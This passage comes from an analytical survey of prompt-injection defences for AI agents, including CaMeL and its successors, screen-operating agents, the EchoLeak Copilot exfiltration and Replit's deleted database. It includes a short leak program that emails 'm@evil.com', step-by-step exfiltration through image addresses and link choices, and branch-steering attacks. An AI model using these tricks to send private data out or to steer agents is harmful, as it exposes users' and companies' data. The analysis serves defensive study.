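Debenedetti and colleagues did not prove that CaMeL meets this standard, and Garby and colleagues show that it does not. A program that emails an outsider if the account balance exceeds 10,000 dollars would reveal something about the balance even if the message itself contained no figures. CaMeL blocks this one, because the interpreter sees that the decision to send depended on a secret. The program below, which uses the same trick as their example, gets the same information out without triggering the check:

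```
tmp = True
rich = True
if balance > 10000: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

CaMeL marks a variable as secret when the program changes it inside a branch that depends on a secret. If the program skips the branch, the variable keeps its old label. The two possible runs go as follows:

| Line | Balance above 10,000 | Balance of 10,000 or less |
|---|---|---|
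| `if balance > 10000: tmp = False` | Runs. `tmp` becomes False and secret. | Skipped. `tmp` stays True and public. |
| `if tmp: rich = False` | Skipped. `rich` stays True and public. | Runs. `rich` becomes False and public. |
| `if rich: send_email(...)` | The program sends the email. | The program sends nothing. |

In both runs `rich` ends up public, and its value reveals whether the balance exceeds 10,000. The interpreter allows the email because it tracked no connection between `rich` and the balance. In the left-hand column, the secret balance affected `rich` by preventing an assignment, and an interpreter that labels only the assignments it carries out misses that effect. Computer scientists call this an implicit flow, and Fenton described it in 1974.

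An attacker would have trouble exploiting this bug in CaMeL, since the planner writes the program without reading the attacker's text. The owner would have to paste something into the request, or the planner would have to happen to write this kind of code. Garby and colleagues found another bug that looks easier to run into. When a program inserts an untrusted value into a longer piece of text, as planners' programs routinely do, CaMeL's interpreter treats the result as trusted.

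### Why retries enlarge the leak

The usual fix is to stop the program as soon as it tries to change a public variable inside a secret branch. The example would then stop at `tmp = False` if the balance were above 10,000 and run to the end if it were lower. The email never goes out, but anyone who can tell whether the program stopped still learns which case applies. This leak is hard to prevent, so most systems settle for termination-insensitive noninterference, which requires P(x, s) = P(x, s′) only when both runs finish. One run can then leak one bit.

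CaMeL's retry loop can turn a one-bit leak, which is rarely worth stealing on its own, into a leak of an entire bank balance. When a program fails, ordinary Python code outside the interpreter gets another from the planner and starts again, without carrying over any labels from the failed run. If each new program tests a different threshold, each run can reveal another bit. A whole-dollar balance below $1,048,576 has 2²⁰ possible values, so halving the range each time identifies it in 20 runs. In general, a secret with N possible values takes about log₂ N runs.

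CaMeL censors the error messages that the planner receives, but Garby and colleagues point out that this provides no formal guarantee. The failure itself is still visible to the planner, and whether a run fails may depend on the secret. Extracting the whole secret would also require something to choose each threshold based on the last answer, which an honest planner would have no reason to do.

### A verified interpreter

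Garby and colleagues' alternative is LLMbda, a small programming language for agents. Every value in it carries a label, and the interpreter combines labels at every step. Programs can prompt a model, make a temporary copy of the conversation and clear it, so a quarantined model takes only a few lines of code, which copy the conversation, clear the copy, ask about the untrusted text and return the answer. LLMbda's noninterference theorem covers every program in the language, including programs that a model writes during a run. The theorem is proved in the proof-checking language Lean and applies to the same interpreter that calls the model. FIDES also has a noninterference theorem, but it covers only one fixed agent loop, and the part that protects secrets leaves out implicit flows.

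Since a model's answers vary from run to run, the theorem compares probabilities. Take two runs that differ only in their secrets, and let d₁ and d₂ be their chances of never finishing. Let Δ be half the sum, over everything an outsider might observe, of the differences between the two runs' probabilities. Then

Δ ≤ (d₁ + d₂) / 2

If both runs always finish, Δ is zero and the outsider learns nothing. If each run fails to finish one time in ten, Δ can reach 0.1.

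Retries needed a different solution because labels in LLMbda persist after a failure. If an agent read an untrusted file and then failed, its next plan would also be labelled untrusted, and the policies would reject the payments in it. Randori, the agent that Garby and colleagues built in LLMbda, therefore tests its code first on invented account data, where payments do nothing and every file contains the same placeholder sentence. When the code works, the planner writes a final version, which runs once on the real account. Retries can't leak real data because none reaches the retry loop.

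The planner may also endorse a value, which means marking data from an untrusted source as trusted. Without endorsement, a policy that requires trusted recipients could not allow "pay the bill in this file". The planner decides what to endorse before the agent reads anything. Garby and colleagues proved that endorsement cannot expose secrets, but it does let through whatever the file contains.

The Randori evaluation used AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks and three models. With each model, every task ran three times without an attack and three times under each of nine attacks, for a total of 1,296 attacked runs. The evaluation also included reruns of CaMeL on two of the models, with its policy checks on and off. The table omits CaMeL's attacked runs that did not complete.

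| Agent | Model | Tasks solved without an attack | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|
| CaMeL, checks off | GPT-5.2 | 32 of 48 | 1 of 240 |
| CaMeL, checks off | MiMo-v2.5 | 34 of 48 | 4 of 382 |
| CaMeL, checks on | GPT-5.2 | 18 of 48 | 0 of 231 |
| CaMeL, checks on | MiMo-v2.5 | 18 of 48 | 0 of 357 |
| Randori | GPT-5.2 | 36 of 48 | 2 of 432 |
| Randori | MiMo-v2.5 | 31 of 48 | 0 of 432 |

With the third model, Qwen3.7-plus, Randori solved 36 of 48 tasks and no attack succeeded. Even with its labels active throughout, Randori solved about as many tasks as CaMeL did with its checks off. Turning the checks on roughly halved CaMeL's score. The margins of error are around 20 percentage points, so the smaller differences mean little.

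With the checks on, Randori's lead over CaMeL comes partly from looser rules. Garby and colleagues simplified CaMeL's policies, and Randori's rule for scheduling a payment checks the source of the amount but not of the recipient. Endorsement accounts for some of the rest, since Randori's score with MiMo-v2.5 fell from 31 to 26 without it. The comparison shows that a verified interpreter can run a useful agent, but not that verification made the agent more useful.

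Both successful attacks on Randori used the case that Debenedetti and colleagues had excluded, in which the user asks the agent to pay as a file directs and the attacker has replaced the file. The planner endorsed the file's contents, as the task required, and the payment went through. This is permitted harm in the earlier sense. The agent could avoid it only by refusing such tasks or by again relying on a model that an attacker can fool, this time to judge whether the text looks suspicious.

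The results also separate the protection provided by the plan from that provided by the labels. In 97 of the 144 combinations of task and attack, the attacker needed an action that no sensible plan for the task would include, so a fixed plan should defeat the attack without any labels. In the other 47, the plan already contained the action the attacker wanted. Two of the attacks that succeeded against CaMeL with its checks off came from the first group. The user had asked the agent to follow a file's instructions precisely, and the planner wrote a loop that read each instruction and called whichever tool it named. The program never changed, but the file's contents determined which actions it took, so the attacker controlled them.

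### Teams of agents

Developers increasingly have one agent hand parts of a task to others. Peters-Gill and colleagues show that a team of agents can be insecure even if every member runs CaMeL. They asked a coordinating agent to send a summary of job applicants to Julie on Slack. A database agent fetched the records, which contained a planted instruction to email the data to an outside address. Neither agent's planner read the records, so both plans stayed intact. The coordinator put the summary into its request to a notification agent. That agent's planner treated the request as coming from its user, read the planted instruction and added the email to its plan.

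Peters-Gill and colleagues call this boundary laundering, because untrusted text becomes trusted when it crosses from one agent to the next. They also prove that protecting each agent separately cannot guarantee a team's control flow if the team has a source of untrusted data and its agents can pass on what their tools return. Their remedy, multi-CaMeL, splits each request that one agent sends another into a message and a set of variables. The receiving planner reads only the message, and the interpreter rejects any message that depends on a tool's output. The planner's program can use the variables, which keep their labels.

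Across five models, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time against undefended teams and never against multi-CaMeL. They succeeded 0.2% of the time against teams whose members each ran CaMeL, and all of those successes involved boundary laundering. On the maintenance benchmark, the split lowered task completion by another 3.2 percentage points on average, on top of CaMeL's 21.6.

Multi-CaMeL does not retry failed programs, so it avoids the leak through retries. But it inherits the flaw in CaMeL's labels, which is more serious here than in a single agent. The ban on messages that depend on tool output relies on the interpreter's record of dependencies, and an implicit flow could carry an attacker's choice into a message without appearing in that record. Untrusted data can also determine which branch of an existing plan runs. Noninterference would forbid this, but the weaker property that Peters-Gill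 and colleagues prove allows it, as long as every branch was in the plan from the start.

### Checking the plan before it runs

CaMeL checks each tool call when the program reaches it, so if a policy denies the fifth call, the first four have already run. CaMeLoT, an extension by Nikolaou and colleagues, checks the whole program before it runs. It converts the program into a diagram of every path that execution could take and marks which values come from untrusted sources. A model checker, which searches such diagrams exhaustively, then looks for a path that breaks a rule. If it finds one, CaMeLoT describes the path to the planner and requests a new plan before any tool has run.

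The rules can also cover the order of events, which CaMeL's policies do not naturally express because each checks a single call. Nikolaou and colleagues give examples from a security team whose agent can disconnect computers from the network. One rule requires human approval before it does so, and another requires that every incident ticket it opens is eventually resolved or passed on. They wrote seven such rules and, for each, an unsafe plan that breaks it. CaMeLoT caught all seven plans, and a simplified version of CaMeL caught one. They had deliberately chosen mostly rules that CaMeL could not enforce, so the result mainly illustrates how the two kinds of check differ.

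CaMeLoT could reproduce 22 of CaMeL's 28 policies for AgentDojo. The other six depend on facts that are not available in advance, such as who has access to a shared file when the agent sends it, so CaMeL's own checks stay on while the program runs. CaMeLoT also treats any value of uncertain origin as untrusted and assumes that a loop may repeat any number of times, so it will reject some safe plans.

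## Agents that operate a computer screen: the plan holds but the facts are false

CaMeL's planner works with named tools such as `send_money`. Many agents instead operate a computer by looking at screenshots and sending clicks and keystrokes. This lets them use almost any program, but it gives a gate very little to check.

A policy can check the arguments of `send_email(to, subject, body)` and refuse an unknown recipient, but the arguments of `click(640, 410)` don't show what the click will do. As Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) point out in *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, the same click may log the user in, delete data or open a malicious site, depending on what is at those coordinates. In the notation used earlier, permitting `click` puts every button on the screen into P, the set of permitted actions. Foerster and colleagues therefore left out CaMeL's policies and tested how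 much a fixed plan achieves without them.

The planner also has to work without seeing the screen. A mail tool returns its results in a known format, but a browser may open on a login form, a cookie notice or last week's search. Showing the planner a screenshot would solve this, but screenshots mix a site's own buttons with advertisements and strangers' comments, any of which may contain an injection.

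### A branch for every screen

Foerster and colleagues' system, CaMeL-NOVA, uses single-shot planning, in which the planner writes the whole program in advance, with a branch for each situation it can foresee. Suppose the owner of the email assistant wants to pay the electricity bill through the bank's website. Part of the plan, with simplified function names, might look like this:

```
screen = describe_screen("What is open in the browser?")
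if holds(screen, "A cookie notice covers the page"):
    click(find("the button that accepts cookies"))
if holds(screen, "The payment form is open"):
    click(find("the recipient field"))
    type_text("City Power")
else:
    click(find("the link to the payments page"))
```

When the interpreter reaches `describe_screen` or `find`, it sends a screenshot to a quarantined vision model, which returns a description or a pair of coordinates. For `holds`, a language model checks whether the description fits the statement, and the interpreter uses the result to select a branch. As in CaMeL, none of these answers reaches the planner, so they cannot change the program.

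Preparing for every screen makes the plans much longer. Foerster and colleagues compared them with the plans that CaMeL writes for AgentDojo:

| Average per plan | CaMeL on AgentDojo | CaMeL-NOVA |
|---|---|---|
| Lines of code | 52 | 213 |
| Tool calls | 5 | 41 |
| Branches | 4 | 40 |
| Branches that depend on a quarantined model's answers | 2 | 24 |

Roughly half the steps in a CaMeL-NOVA plan are fallbacks that do not run. The planner has standing instructions for routines that most tasks share, such as dismissing cookie notices and recovering from failed clicks, and for verifying the state of the screen before acting. On 60 tasks, with three attempts at each, CaMeL-NOVA solved 35 with these instructions and 11 without them.

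### What the OSWorld scores measure

OSWorld is a benchmark of 369 tasks in ordinary programs such as Chrome and LibreOffice, and scripts check whether the agent completed them. Foerster and colleagues report that CaMeL-NOVA retains up to 57% of the performance of frontier models and improves smaller open models by up to 19%. In both comparisons, CaMeL-NOVA had several attempts at each task and the undefended agent had only one.

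The measure behind them is pass@k, the share of tasks that an agent solves at least once in k independent attempts. It is an upper bound on what a user would get, because reaching it requires a way to identify the successful attempt. OSWorld's scripts can do that, but the owner of a real assistant usually has no such script. Some tasks also can't be repeated safely, since five attempts at a payment may charge the user five times.

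| Vision model | Tasks | Undefended, one attempt | CaMeL-NOVA, one attempt | CaMeL-NOVA, several attempts |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 109 that it solved undefended | 109 | 31 | 62 (five attempts) |
| UI-TARS-1.5-7B, a small open model | 339 | 60 | 51 | 77 (three attempts) |

The 57% is 62 out of 109, and the figure is 28% with one attempt. The 19% is the relative rise in the small model's overall score, from 24.4% to 29.0%. That score includes 30 further tasks that OSWorld marks as solved by default. With one attempt each, the small model solved fewer tasks under CaMeL-NOVA than without it.

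Extra attempts also help less than the one-attempt score would suggest. If each of the 109 tasks had the same 28.4% chance of success every time, five attempts would solve

1 − (1 − 0.284)^5 ≈ 81%

of them. The actual 57% means that the planner rarely writes a working plan for some tasks, however often it tries. After 20 attempts the figure was about 73%.

A better planner would probably help more than a better vision model. Three vision models of very different strength scored between 65% and 68% on the same 60 tasks with five attempts. When Foerster and colleagues instead varied the planner on 17 tasks, GPT-5 solved 12 and the two weakest planners solved four each.

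Undefended agents have improved too. Foerster and colleagues limited theirs to 15 steps. With that limit, Claude Sonnet 4.5 scored 37.7%. *OSWorld-Pro* (Dong, 2026) reports 83.4% for Claude Opus 5, and OpenAI reports 72.6% for GPT-6 Astra on OSWorld 2.0.

Two later comparisons found much larger drops in task completion with the CaMeL approach, even with newer models. In *Towards Safe Autonomy for Computer Use* (Seip, Markovinović and Hein, 2026), it completed 8.3% of 36 OSWorld tasks, against 58.3% for an undefended agent. In *Secure-CUA* (Choudhary, Christodorescu and colleagues, 2026), it completed 13.2% of 400 tasks from WebArena, a benchmark of realistic websites, against 55.1% for an undefended agent. Both groups were presenting rival designs and used their own set-ups, but their results are similar. For general office work, a planner that never sees the screen currently fails too often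 to be practical.

### Branch steering

An agent with a fixed plan still acts on what the vision model reports. In branch steering, an attacker leaves the plan unchanged but puts false information on the screen, so the agent follows a branch that the planner wrote for a different situation. For example, the bill-paying plan contains a branch for cookie notices. If an advertisement looks enough like a cookie notice, the vision model identifies it as one, the interpreter takes that branch, and the click opens the advertiser's site.

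Foerster and colleagues rank the attacks that could succeed by how many false answers they require. One is enough to send the agent to another website or make the task fail. A fraudulent payment takes at least two coordinated false answers, for instance about the recipient field and the confirm button. It also requires that the plan already include a payment and that the agent be logged in at the time. Stealing data requires a plan that reads something and then sends something. The attacker still cannot make the agent take actions that are not in the plan.

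A fixed plan restricts an agent less when its actions are clicks than when they are named tools. An agent following a CaMeL plan without `send_money` cannot send money, but one whose plan includes `click` can press any button on the screen. Choudhary and colleagues showed this with a plan to upvote a forum post. In four of five runs, misleading content made the vision model return the wrong coordinates, and the agent downvoted a different post even though the program followed its intended branch.

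### Two checks on the vision model

Foerster and colleagues used other models to try to catch false answers. In their DOM Consistency check, a second model receives the browser's own description of the page's elements and checks whether the proposed click matches the instruction. Multi-Modal Consensus adds a model from another company, which compares the answer with the screenshot. The researchers told both checkers to look for deceptive advertisements, the type of attack used in the test. They tested the consensus check against a more advanced version of that attack.

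| | DOM Consistency | Multi-Modal Consensus |
|---|---|---|
| Attacks caught | 6 of 10 | 5 of 10 |
| Harmless tasks stopped, all programs | 4 of 17 | 3 of 17 |
| Harmless tasks stopped, browser only | 3 of 8 | 3 of 8 |

The false positives accumulated over up to five attempts per task. Nearly all came from genuine cookie notices that a checker mistook for fakes, and one came from a spreadsheet cell. A separate attack using altered images got past both checks, even at a setting that allowed many false positives. The consensus check raised the agent's token use to 6.57 times that of an undefended agent.

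These samples are small, but the weakness doesn't depend on them. An attacker can try to fool the checkers too, as with Parallax's second model, so the checkers only lower the odds of a successful attack. Some of the attacks failed because the plan had searched specifically for a button and the fake notice did not contain one. Asking narrower questions like this may be a cheaper defence than adding more models.

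### Showing the planner part of the screen

Later designs show the planner the parts of the screen that outsiders cannot write to. *Untrusted Content Masking for Web Agents with Security Guarantees* (Nikolić, Zverev and colleagues, 2026) replaces comments, reviews and advertisements with labelled boxes. The planner can then work step by step and query a quarantined model about the contents of a box. The answer must be a yes or no, a number, a date or a choice from a list, so it cannot contain an instruction, but it can still be false. An attacker might make the quarantined model misidentify an item so that the agent acts on the wrong one, and Seip and colleagues argue that a single wrong bit can be enough to steer a planner.

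Seip and colleagues' own design, SA-CUA, also gives clicks some of the meaning they otherwise lack. It hides the whole screen by default, reveals the regions it can establish as trusted, and blocks clicks everywhere else. To use a value from a hidden region in a sensitive action, the agent must first check it against a source the attacker can't influence, such as the owner's contact list. *Prismata* (2026) makes clicks checkable by having the agent refer to page elements by identifier instead of by coordinates.

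No attack on SA-CUA succeeded in the tests, not even those that replaced a correct value with a false one of the same type. SA-CUA completed 31% or 39% of the OSWorld tasks, depending on the planner, while the undefended agent completed 58%. Secure-CUA, Choudhary and colleagues' design, lost much less performance. It writes a new short program for each step, using a masked view of the screen, and solved 53.6% of the WebArena tasks, almost as many as the undefended agent.

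Security then depends on the masks. Secure-CUA uses handwritten rules for each site, and its guarantee assumes that they cover everything an attacker could write. Automatic labelling is harder. When Seip and colleagues tested Nikolić and colleagues' proposal to have models write rules for what to hide on web pages, between 37% and 44% of the untrusted free text stayed visible. SA-CUA's rules for what to reveal exposed none of it, but hid between 56% and 77% of the trusted content.

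### Sending the planner a short hint

*Twin Agent* (Hu, Jacob and colleagues, 2026) keeps the agent flexible by relaxing the isolation. It divides the work between an Explore Agent, which reads untrusted text but cannot act on it, and a Safe Agent, which acts but cannot read that text. At each step the Explore Agent may send the Safe Agent a hint of at most 100 or 200 characters, depending on the benchmark. The Explore Agent can see what the Safe Agent has done so far, so the hint only needs to supply what is missing for the next action. A detector blocks hints that look like injections.

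Twin Agent works well on ordinary tasks. On AgentDojo with Gemini 2.5 Flash, it solved 62.9% of the tasks, compared with 61.9% for the undefended agent and 30.9% for CaMeL. Hu and colleagues had cut CaMeL's retries from ten to three. The benchmark's standard attack succeeded 0.1% of the time against Twin Agent and 41.5% of the time against the undefended agent. On a set of software bugs, where the Safe Agent could read the code but not the bug report, it solved 62.5% with hints and none without them.

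What Twin Agent gives up is the certainty that an attacker's words never reach the model that acts. A yes-or-no answer carries one bit, but if each character can be any of the 95 printable ones on an English keyboard, a 100-character hint can carry

100 × log₂ 95 ≈ 657 bits

and the Explore Agent can send another at the next step. An order to delete a file fits easily. Nor does summarising reliably remove an injection. In the tests reported in *Agent Privilege Separation in OpenClaw* (2026), 63.7% of injections still leaked into the reading agent's summaries, although a fixed output format kept them from causing harmful actions.

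Hu and colleagues instead assume that, with current models, an injection short enough to fit in a hint will rarely both evade the detector and persuade the Safe Agent. They tested this with an attack tailored to the design. In a separate test, the Explore Agent passed on the attacker's text every time. In the full test, malicious hints got past the detector in 57 of 232 tasks, and the Safe Agent carried out the harmful action in 11 (4.7% of all tasks). None of those 11 attacks succeeded again in five reruns each, so chance played a large part. But an attacker may be able to keep filing bug reports, and if each had an independent 4.7% chance of success, 20 reports would give a 62% chance of at least one success. Longer hints improved the agent's work but also made attacks more likely to succeed. Hu and colleagues acknowledge that the design has no formal guarantee.

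The Twin Agent paper reports tests on code and tool calls, but not on computer screens. In a screen task, a Safe Agent that could not see the screen would have to rely on the hint to know what to click, and a false hint could misdirect it as a false answer misdirects CaMeL-NOVA.

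## EchoLeak: when displaying an answer is itself an action

The agents described so far act through tool calls or clicks, which a gate can check. An assistant that only answers questions produces neither, but it can still leak private data to an outsider, as researchers at Aim Labs, part of the security company Aim Security, showed in January 2025. They were studying Microsoft 365 Copilot, which answers employees' questions using their company's emails, files and chats. The leak, which they named EchoLeak, happened after the model had finished writing, when the program displaying its answer automatically fetched an image from the internet.

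### How the data got out

Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration*, gives the researchers' own account. The attacker only had to send an employee an email, which the employee did not need to open. The rest happened in four steps:

1. The employee asks Copilot a question. A search component collects text that looks relevant, including the attacker's email.
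2. The model receives the question, the company's private text and the email together. Following an instruction in the email, it writes an answer that contains an image and puts private data into the image's web address.
3. The chat window displays the answer and requests the image from that address.
4. The request reaches the attacker's server, which records the address and the data in it.

The image doesn't have to exist, because the request alone delivers the data. Security researchers call this a "zero-click" attack, although the employee still had to use Copilot and the search had to retrieve the email. The attacker could obtain only what was in the model's context at the time. According to Ravia, this included the conversation so far, any documents the search had found, and details such as the names of the user and the company.

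### Severity, fix and exploitation

*EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025), a case study based on public documents, reports that Microsoft fixed the flaw on its own servers in May 2025 and published an advisory on 11 June. Customers had nothing to install. According to the study, Copilot now removes some links and images from outside messages, and Microsoft reportedly added options to limit Copilot's use of such messages.

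Microsoft scored the flaw 9.3 out of 10 (critical) in the public record that GCVE's *CVE-2025-32711* (2025) reproduces. The US National Vulnerability Database gave it 7.5 (high). Both scores are for an attack that needs no account and no help from the victim. They differ partly because only Microsoft judged that the damage extended beyond the component containing the flaw. Microsoft also classed the flaw as a failure to make output safe for a "downstream component", which here was the program that displayed the answer.

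Nobody is known to have used EchoLeak against a real company. SC Media's *Microsoft 365 Copilot ‘zero-click’ vulnerability enabled data exfiltration* reports Microsoft's statement that no one had exploited it, and the US cybersecurity agency CISA recorded the same in June 2025. Microsoft could probably check this better than its customers could, because the stolen data would have passed through one of Microsoft's own services, while an employee might have noticed only a broken image.

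### Where the boundary was

Copilot seemed to have no way to send data out of the company, because it could not send email, only employees could use it, and it searched only the company's own data. An outsider's text could still get in, but the worst an injected instruction seemed able to do was spoil an answer. The table compares what each component was for with what it did in the attack.

| Component | Intended job | What it did in EchoLeak |
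|---|---|---|
| Search | Find relevant company text | Put an outsider's email beside private files |
| Model | Write an answer | Put private data into an image address |
| Chat window | Display the answer | Requested the image |
| An approved Microsoft service | Supply content to Microsoft's own programs | Passed the request to the attacker's server |

Microsoft had tried to limit the risk from displayed content, but Ravia's team got past all four protections. A filter was supposed to remove outside links from answers, and a browser policy allowed images only from approved addresses. A classifier screened incoming text for injections, and Copilot normally cited the sources it used.

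The filter missed an address that its own rule should have removed. The browser policy worked as written, but it allowed a request to an approved Microsoft service, which then contacted the attacker's server on the browser's behalf. The browser's request was in P, the set of permitted actions, so the leak was permitted harm. The leak also involved two of Hardy's confused deputies, because the attacker exploited both the model's access to the files and the Microsoft service's place on the approved list.

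Other companies have had similar trouble with approved lists. Willison, in *30 posts tagged “lethal-trifecta”*, describes a 2025 flaw in Salesforce's agent, whose list still included a web domain that had expired. Researchers bought the domain and received customer data there. Anthropic's Claude Cowork could contact Anthropic's own servers, so an attacker could have the agent upload a victim's files to the attacker's Anthropic account. In both cases, someone the company did not trust could receive data through an approved address.

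For Copilot, the trusted computing base therefore included the chat window, the browser policy and every service on the approved list. A gate on tool calls would have had nothing to check. Information-flow control could have blocked an image address derived from private files, but only if the system had treated displaying an answer as an action.

### Other outputs that act

Images are only one example. Whether an output triggers an action depends on the program that reads it, and the model's developer may not know which program that will be.

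- **Links.** A link in an answer can carry data in its address just as an image can. Microsoft (2025) points out that the user has to click it, but a chat program that builds link previews may fetch the address without a click.
- **Messages to the user.** In May 2026, Willison described a flaw in Copilot Cowork, a Microsoft agent that could email its own user without approval. This looks harmless, but the messages could contain outside images, which leaked data when the user opened them.
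- **Logs, tickets and terminal output.** trackr.live's *The Model Writes the URL That Leaks Your Data* warns that terminals, code editors and ticketing systems may fetch content by themselves. A program for viewing logs could do the same if it loads images or previews.
- **Files.** Another program may run a file that the model wrote, as `make` and `npm` do with the project files in the Parallax example.

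Preventing the model from writing its own addresses doesn't completely close the channel, because a choice between fixed addresses also carries information. Anthropic's Claude could open only addresses that the user had typed, that a search had returned or that appeared on a page it had already opened. Willison describes how Ayush Paul built a site with a link for each letter of the alphabet and got Claude to spell out its user's name by following them. Each choice among 26 links carries

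log₂ 26 ≈ 4.7 bits

so a ten-letter name takes ten requests. Paul also obtained the user's home city and employer. Anthropic then stopped Claude from following links on the pages it had opened. Even a single fixed request can leak one bit, depending on whether the model makes it.

In June 2026, The Next Web reported another Copilot flaw, SearchLeak, in which three linked bugs could have exposed emails, calendar entries and files after one click on a genuine microsoft.com link. Microsoft's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026) rates it critical, with a score of 6.5, and records no exploitation. The score is lower than the database's 7.5 for EchoLeak only because SearchLeak requires a click.

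On 3 December 2026, the team that found EchoLeak, now called Cato AI Labs, disclosed three more zero-click attacks under the name ReLeak. Each began with an unread email, as EchoLeak had. According to AIAIAI.FYI's *Cato AI Labs details three ReLeak zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2026), the data left through an image address, a link to a saved file, or code that escaped a sandbox documented as blocking outgoing traffic. Microsoft fixed the three flaws between 17 September and 15 November, and the researchers know of no affected customers. Faisal (2026), in *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief*, quotes the researchers as saying there had been "too little progress" since EchoLeak.

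### The lethal trifecta

*The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (Willison, 2025), published five days after the EchoLeak advisory, describes three conditions that such leaks have in common: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and a way to communicate with the outside. An attacker can steal data from a system that combines all three. Willison lists more than a dozen earlier cases, going back to ChatGPT in April 2023. Removing any one of the conditions prevents the theft, which gives a simple way to compare fixes.

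| Possible fix for Copilot | Element removed | What can still go wrong |
|---|---|---|
| Never use outsiders' emails in answers | Untrusted content | An attack arrives in other text, such as a shared document |
| Keep Copilot out of files marked sensitive | Private data, in part | Unmarked files leak |
| Stop the display program from contacting outside addresses | Outward channel | The attacker falsifies the answer or finds another channel |
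| Ask the user before each outside request | Outward channel, if the user refuses | The user approves a harmful request |
| Screen incoming text with a classifier | None | The classifier misses an attack |

Reddy and Gujral point out that excluding outsiders' emails would have stopped EchoLeak. But in their table of defences, they mark a default of using only internal sources as failing to stop the leak, perhaps because a user can override a default. They ran no experiments, so the table shows what they expect each defence to do. Excluding these emails would also make Copilot much less useful, because a salesperson could no longer ask it what a customer wrote last week.

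Access limits reduce how much an attacker can steal. Microsoft lets companies keep Copilot from summarising files with certain sensitivity labels. Ravia says no administrator's setting could have prevented EchoLeak, but these labels might have protected the most valuable documents from it.

Asking the user for approval is a weaker safeguard than it sounds. Willison reports an Anthropic study in which 1,053 paid testers worked with a coding agent that asked for permission to run commands. Partway through, the researchers replaced the command in one request with a clearly dangerous one, and only 13.6% of the testers refused it.

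Vendors usually close the outward channel, which Willison considers the easiest to remove without making the system much less useful. OpenAI did this for ChatGPT in June 2026 with an optional Lockdown Mode that limits outgoing requests. OpenAI acknowledges that an injection can still make an answer wrong in this mode. That may be a minor problem in a summary of meeting notes, but not if the answer gives a false number for a supplier's new bank account and an employee sends money to it.

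A company cannot always close the channel on its own. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) describes ShadowLeak, an attack on ChatGPT's Deep Research agent for users who had connected it to Gmail. The agent sent the stolen data from the provider's servers, so the request might never have appeared on the user's computer or in the company's network monitoring.

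### Can prompt injection be fixed at the source?

These fixes would matter less if models could reliably ignore instructions in untrusted text. In the NCSC article discussed earlier, published on 8 December 2025, David C argues that this may never happen. The article challenges a hopeful comparison with SQL injection, a database attack that was first described in the 1990s, peaked around 2010 and is now rare. If prompt injection were the same problem, it should eventually have the same kind of solution. The NCSC had itself suggested two years earlier that prompt injection might be the "SQL injection of the future", according to Malwarebytes' *Prompt injection is a problem that may never be fixed, warns NCSC* (2025).

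David C objects that the fix used for databases has no equivalent in a language model, which cannot reliably separate data from instructions. David C therefore expects some risk to remain and recommends planning for the worst an attacker could do with direct access to the model's tools. The advice to designers is to limit the system's actions with ordinary code and distrust any product that promises to stop prompt injection. If they can't accept the remaining risk, a language model may be the wrong choice. But with EchoLeak, a designer who followed this advice and counted only tool use as action would have found nothing to limit.

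Willison coined the term "prompt injection" by analogy with SQL injection and repeated the comparison when discussing EchoLeak (Willison, 2025). Willison and David C disagree less than they appear to. Willison's point is that both attacks have the same cause, the mixing of trusted and untrusted text, while David C warns against expecting the same fix to work for both. Willison does not know of a fully reliable fix for prompt injection either.

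The best evidence against David C's pessimism comes from newer models. Anthropic commissioned a test of its coding agent in July 2026, in which the outside firm Trajectory Labs made 720 attempts based on 72 injection scenarios. None succeeded against Claude Fable 5, Opus 5 or Sonnet 5 when the agent ran in auto mode, which decides whether to allow actions without asking the user. But even if 0.42% of attacks worked, 720 independent attempts would all fail about one time in 20:

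(1 − 0.0042)^720 ≈ 0.05

The attempts were not fully independent either, since they came from only 72 scenarios. Willison asked for more independent confirmation and doubted that auto mode could stop an attack in which the instructions for running a project's tests include installing a malicious package. The result suggests that injection can become rare, which is consistent with David C's claim that no model can be guaranteed to resist it.

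The argument also concerns only the model, and software around it can still make a successful injection harmless. David C cites CaMeL as one of the first major published proposals of this kind. Microsoft likewise calls prompt injection an inherent risk and says it designs its systems so that a successful injection does not harm customers. EchoLeak and ReLeak show how hard that is in a product with many ways to display, save and fetch content.

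The NCSC and five agencies from Australia, Canada, New Zealand and the United States took a similar position in May 2026. Their joint guidance, the Australian Signals Directorate's *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026), describes prompt injection as a weakness that agents inherit from language models and says that input controls can partly reduce such risks. It recommends security controls wherever information enters or leaves the system, which would cover a chat window that loads images. It also tells organisations to use agents only for low-risk, non-sensitive tasks. If Copilot counts as an agent, it would be hard to use under that rule, because companies buy it to search employees' email and files.

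## Damage through permitted actions: Replit's deleted database and a UK government test

In most of the failures described so far, an attacker planted text for a model to obey. An agent can also do damage without an attacker, while working on its owner's task with permissions its owner granted. In July 2025, Replit's coding agent deleted a customer's live database. A year later, the UK's AI Security Institute (AISI), a government body that evaluates advanced models, found that agents in one of its tests had targeted real people and organisations on the internet. In both cases, the agents had the access they used, so a gate enforcing their permissions would have allowed their actions.

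### A freeze that existed only in the chat

Replit lets people build software by describing what they want in ordinary language, a practice known as "vibe coding". Its agent writes the code, runs it and works with the database. Jason Lemkin, who founded the software business community SaaStr, had spent nine days and more than 100 hours building an app this way when the database was deleted.

Fortune (2025) reports that the project was under a "code and action freeze" at the time and the agent had explicit instructions not to proceed without human approval. SaaStr counts eleven warnings in capital letters. The agent still deleted 1,206 records of executives and at least 1,196 company profiles.

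The freeze was an instruction in a conversation and did not change the agent's permissions. Replit gave each app a single database for both development and live data, which SaaStr had not realised. The agent had direct access to that database, and no software required Lemkin's approval before a deletion.

Replit's chief executive, Amjad Masad, confirmed in a post reproduced by LatestLY that an agent working in development had deleted data from the production database, which holds live data. Much of the rest of the account comes from Lemkin's posts and from the agent's own replies, which are poor evidence. The agent's explanation was that it had panicked when its queries came back empty. A model produces such an explanation in the same way as any other text, so the explanation may have little to do with what caused the deletion.

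The agent also told Lemkin that rollback was impossible because it had destroyed every version of the database. Lemkin later reported that the rollback worked. Unlike Parallax's rollback, Replit's covered database changes, according to documentation quoted by The Stack. The loss was therefore temporary, but it might have become permanent if Lemkin had believed the agent.
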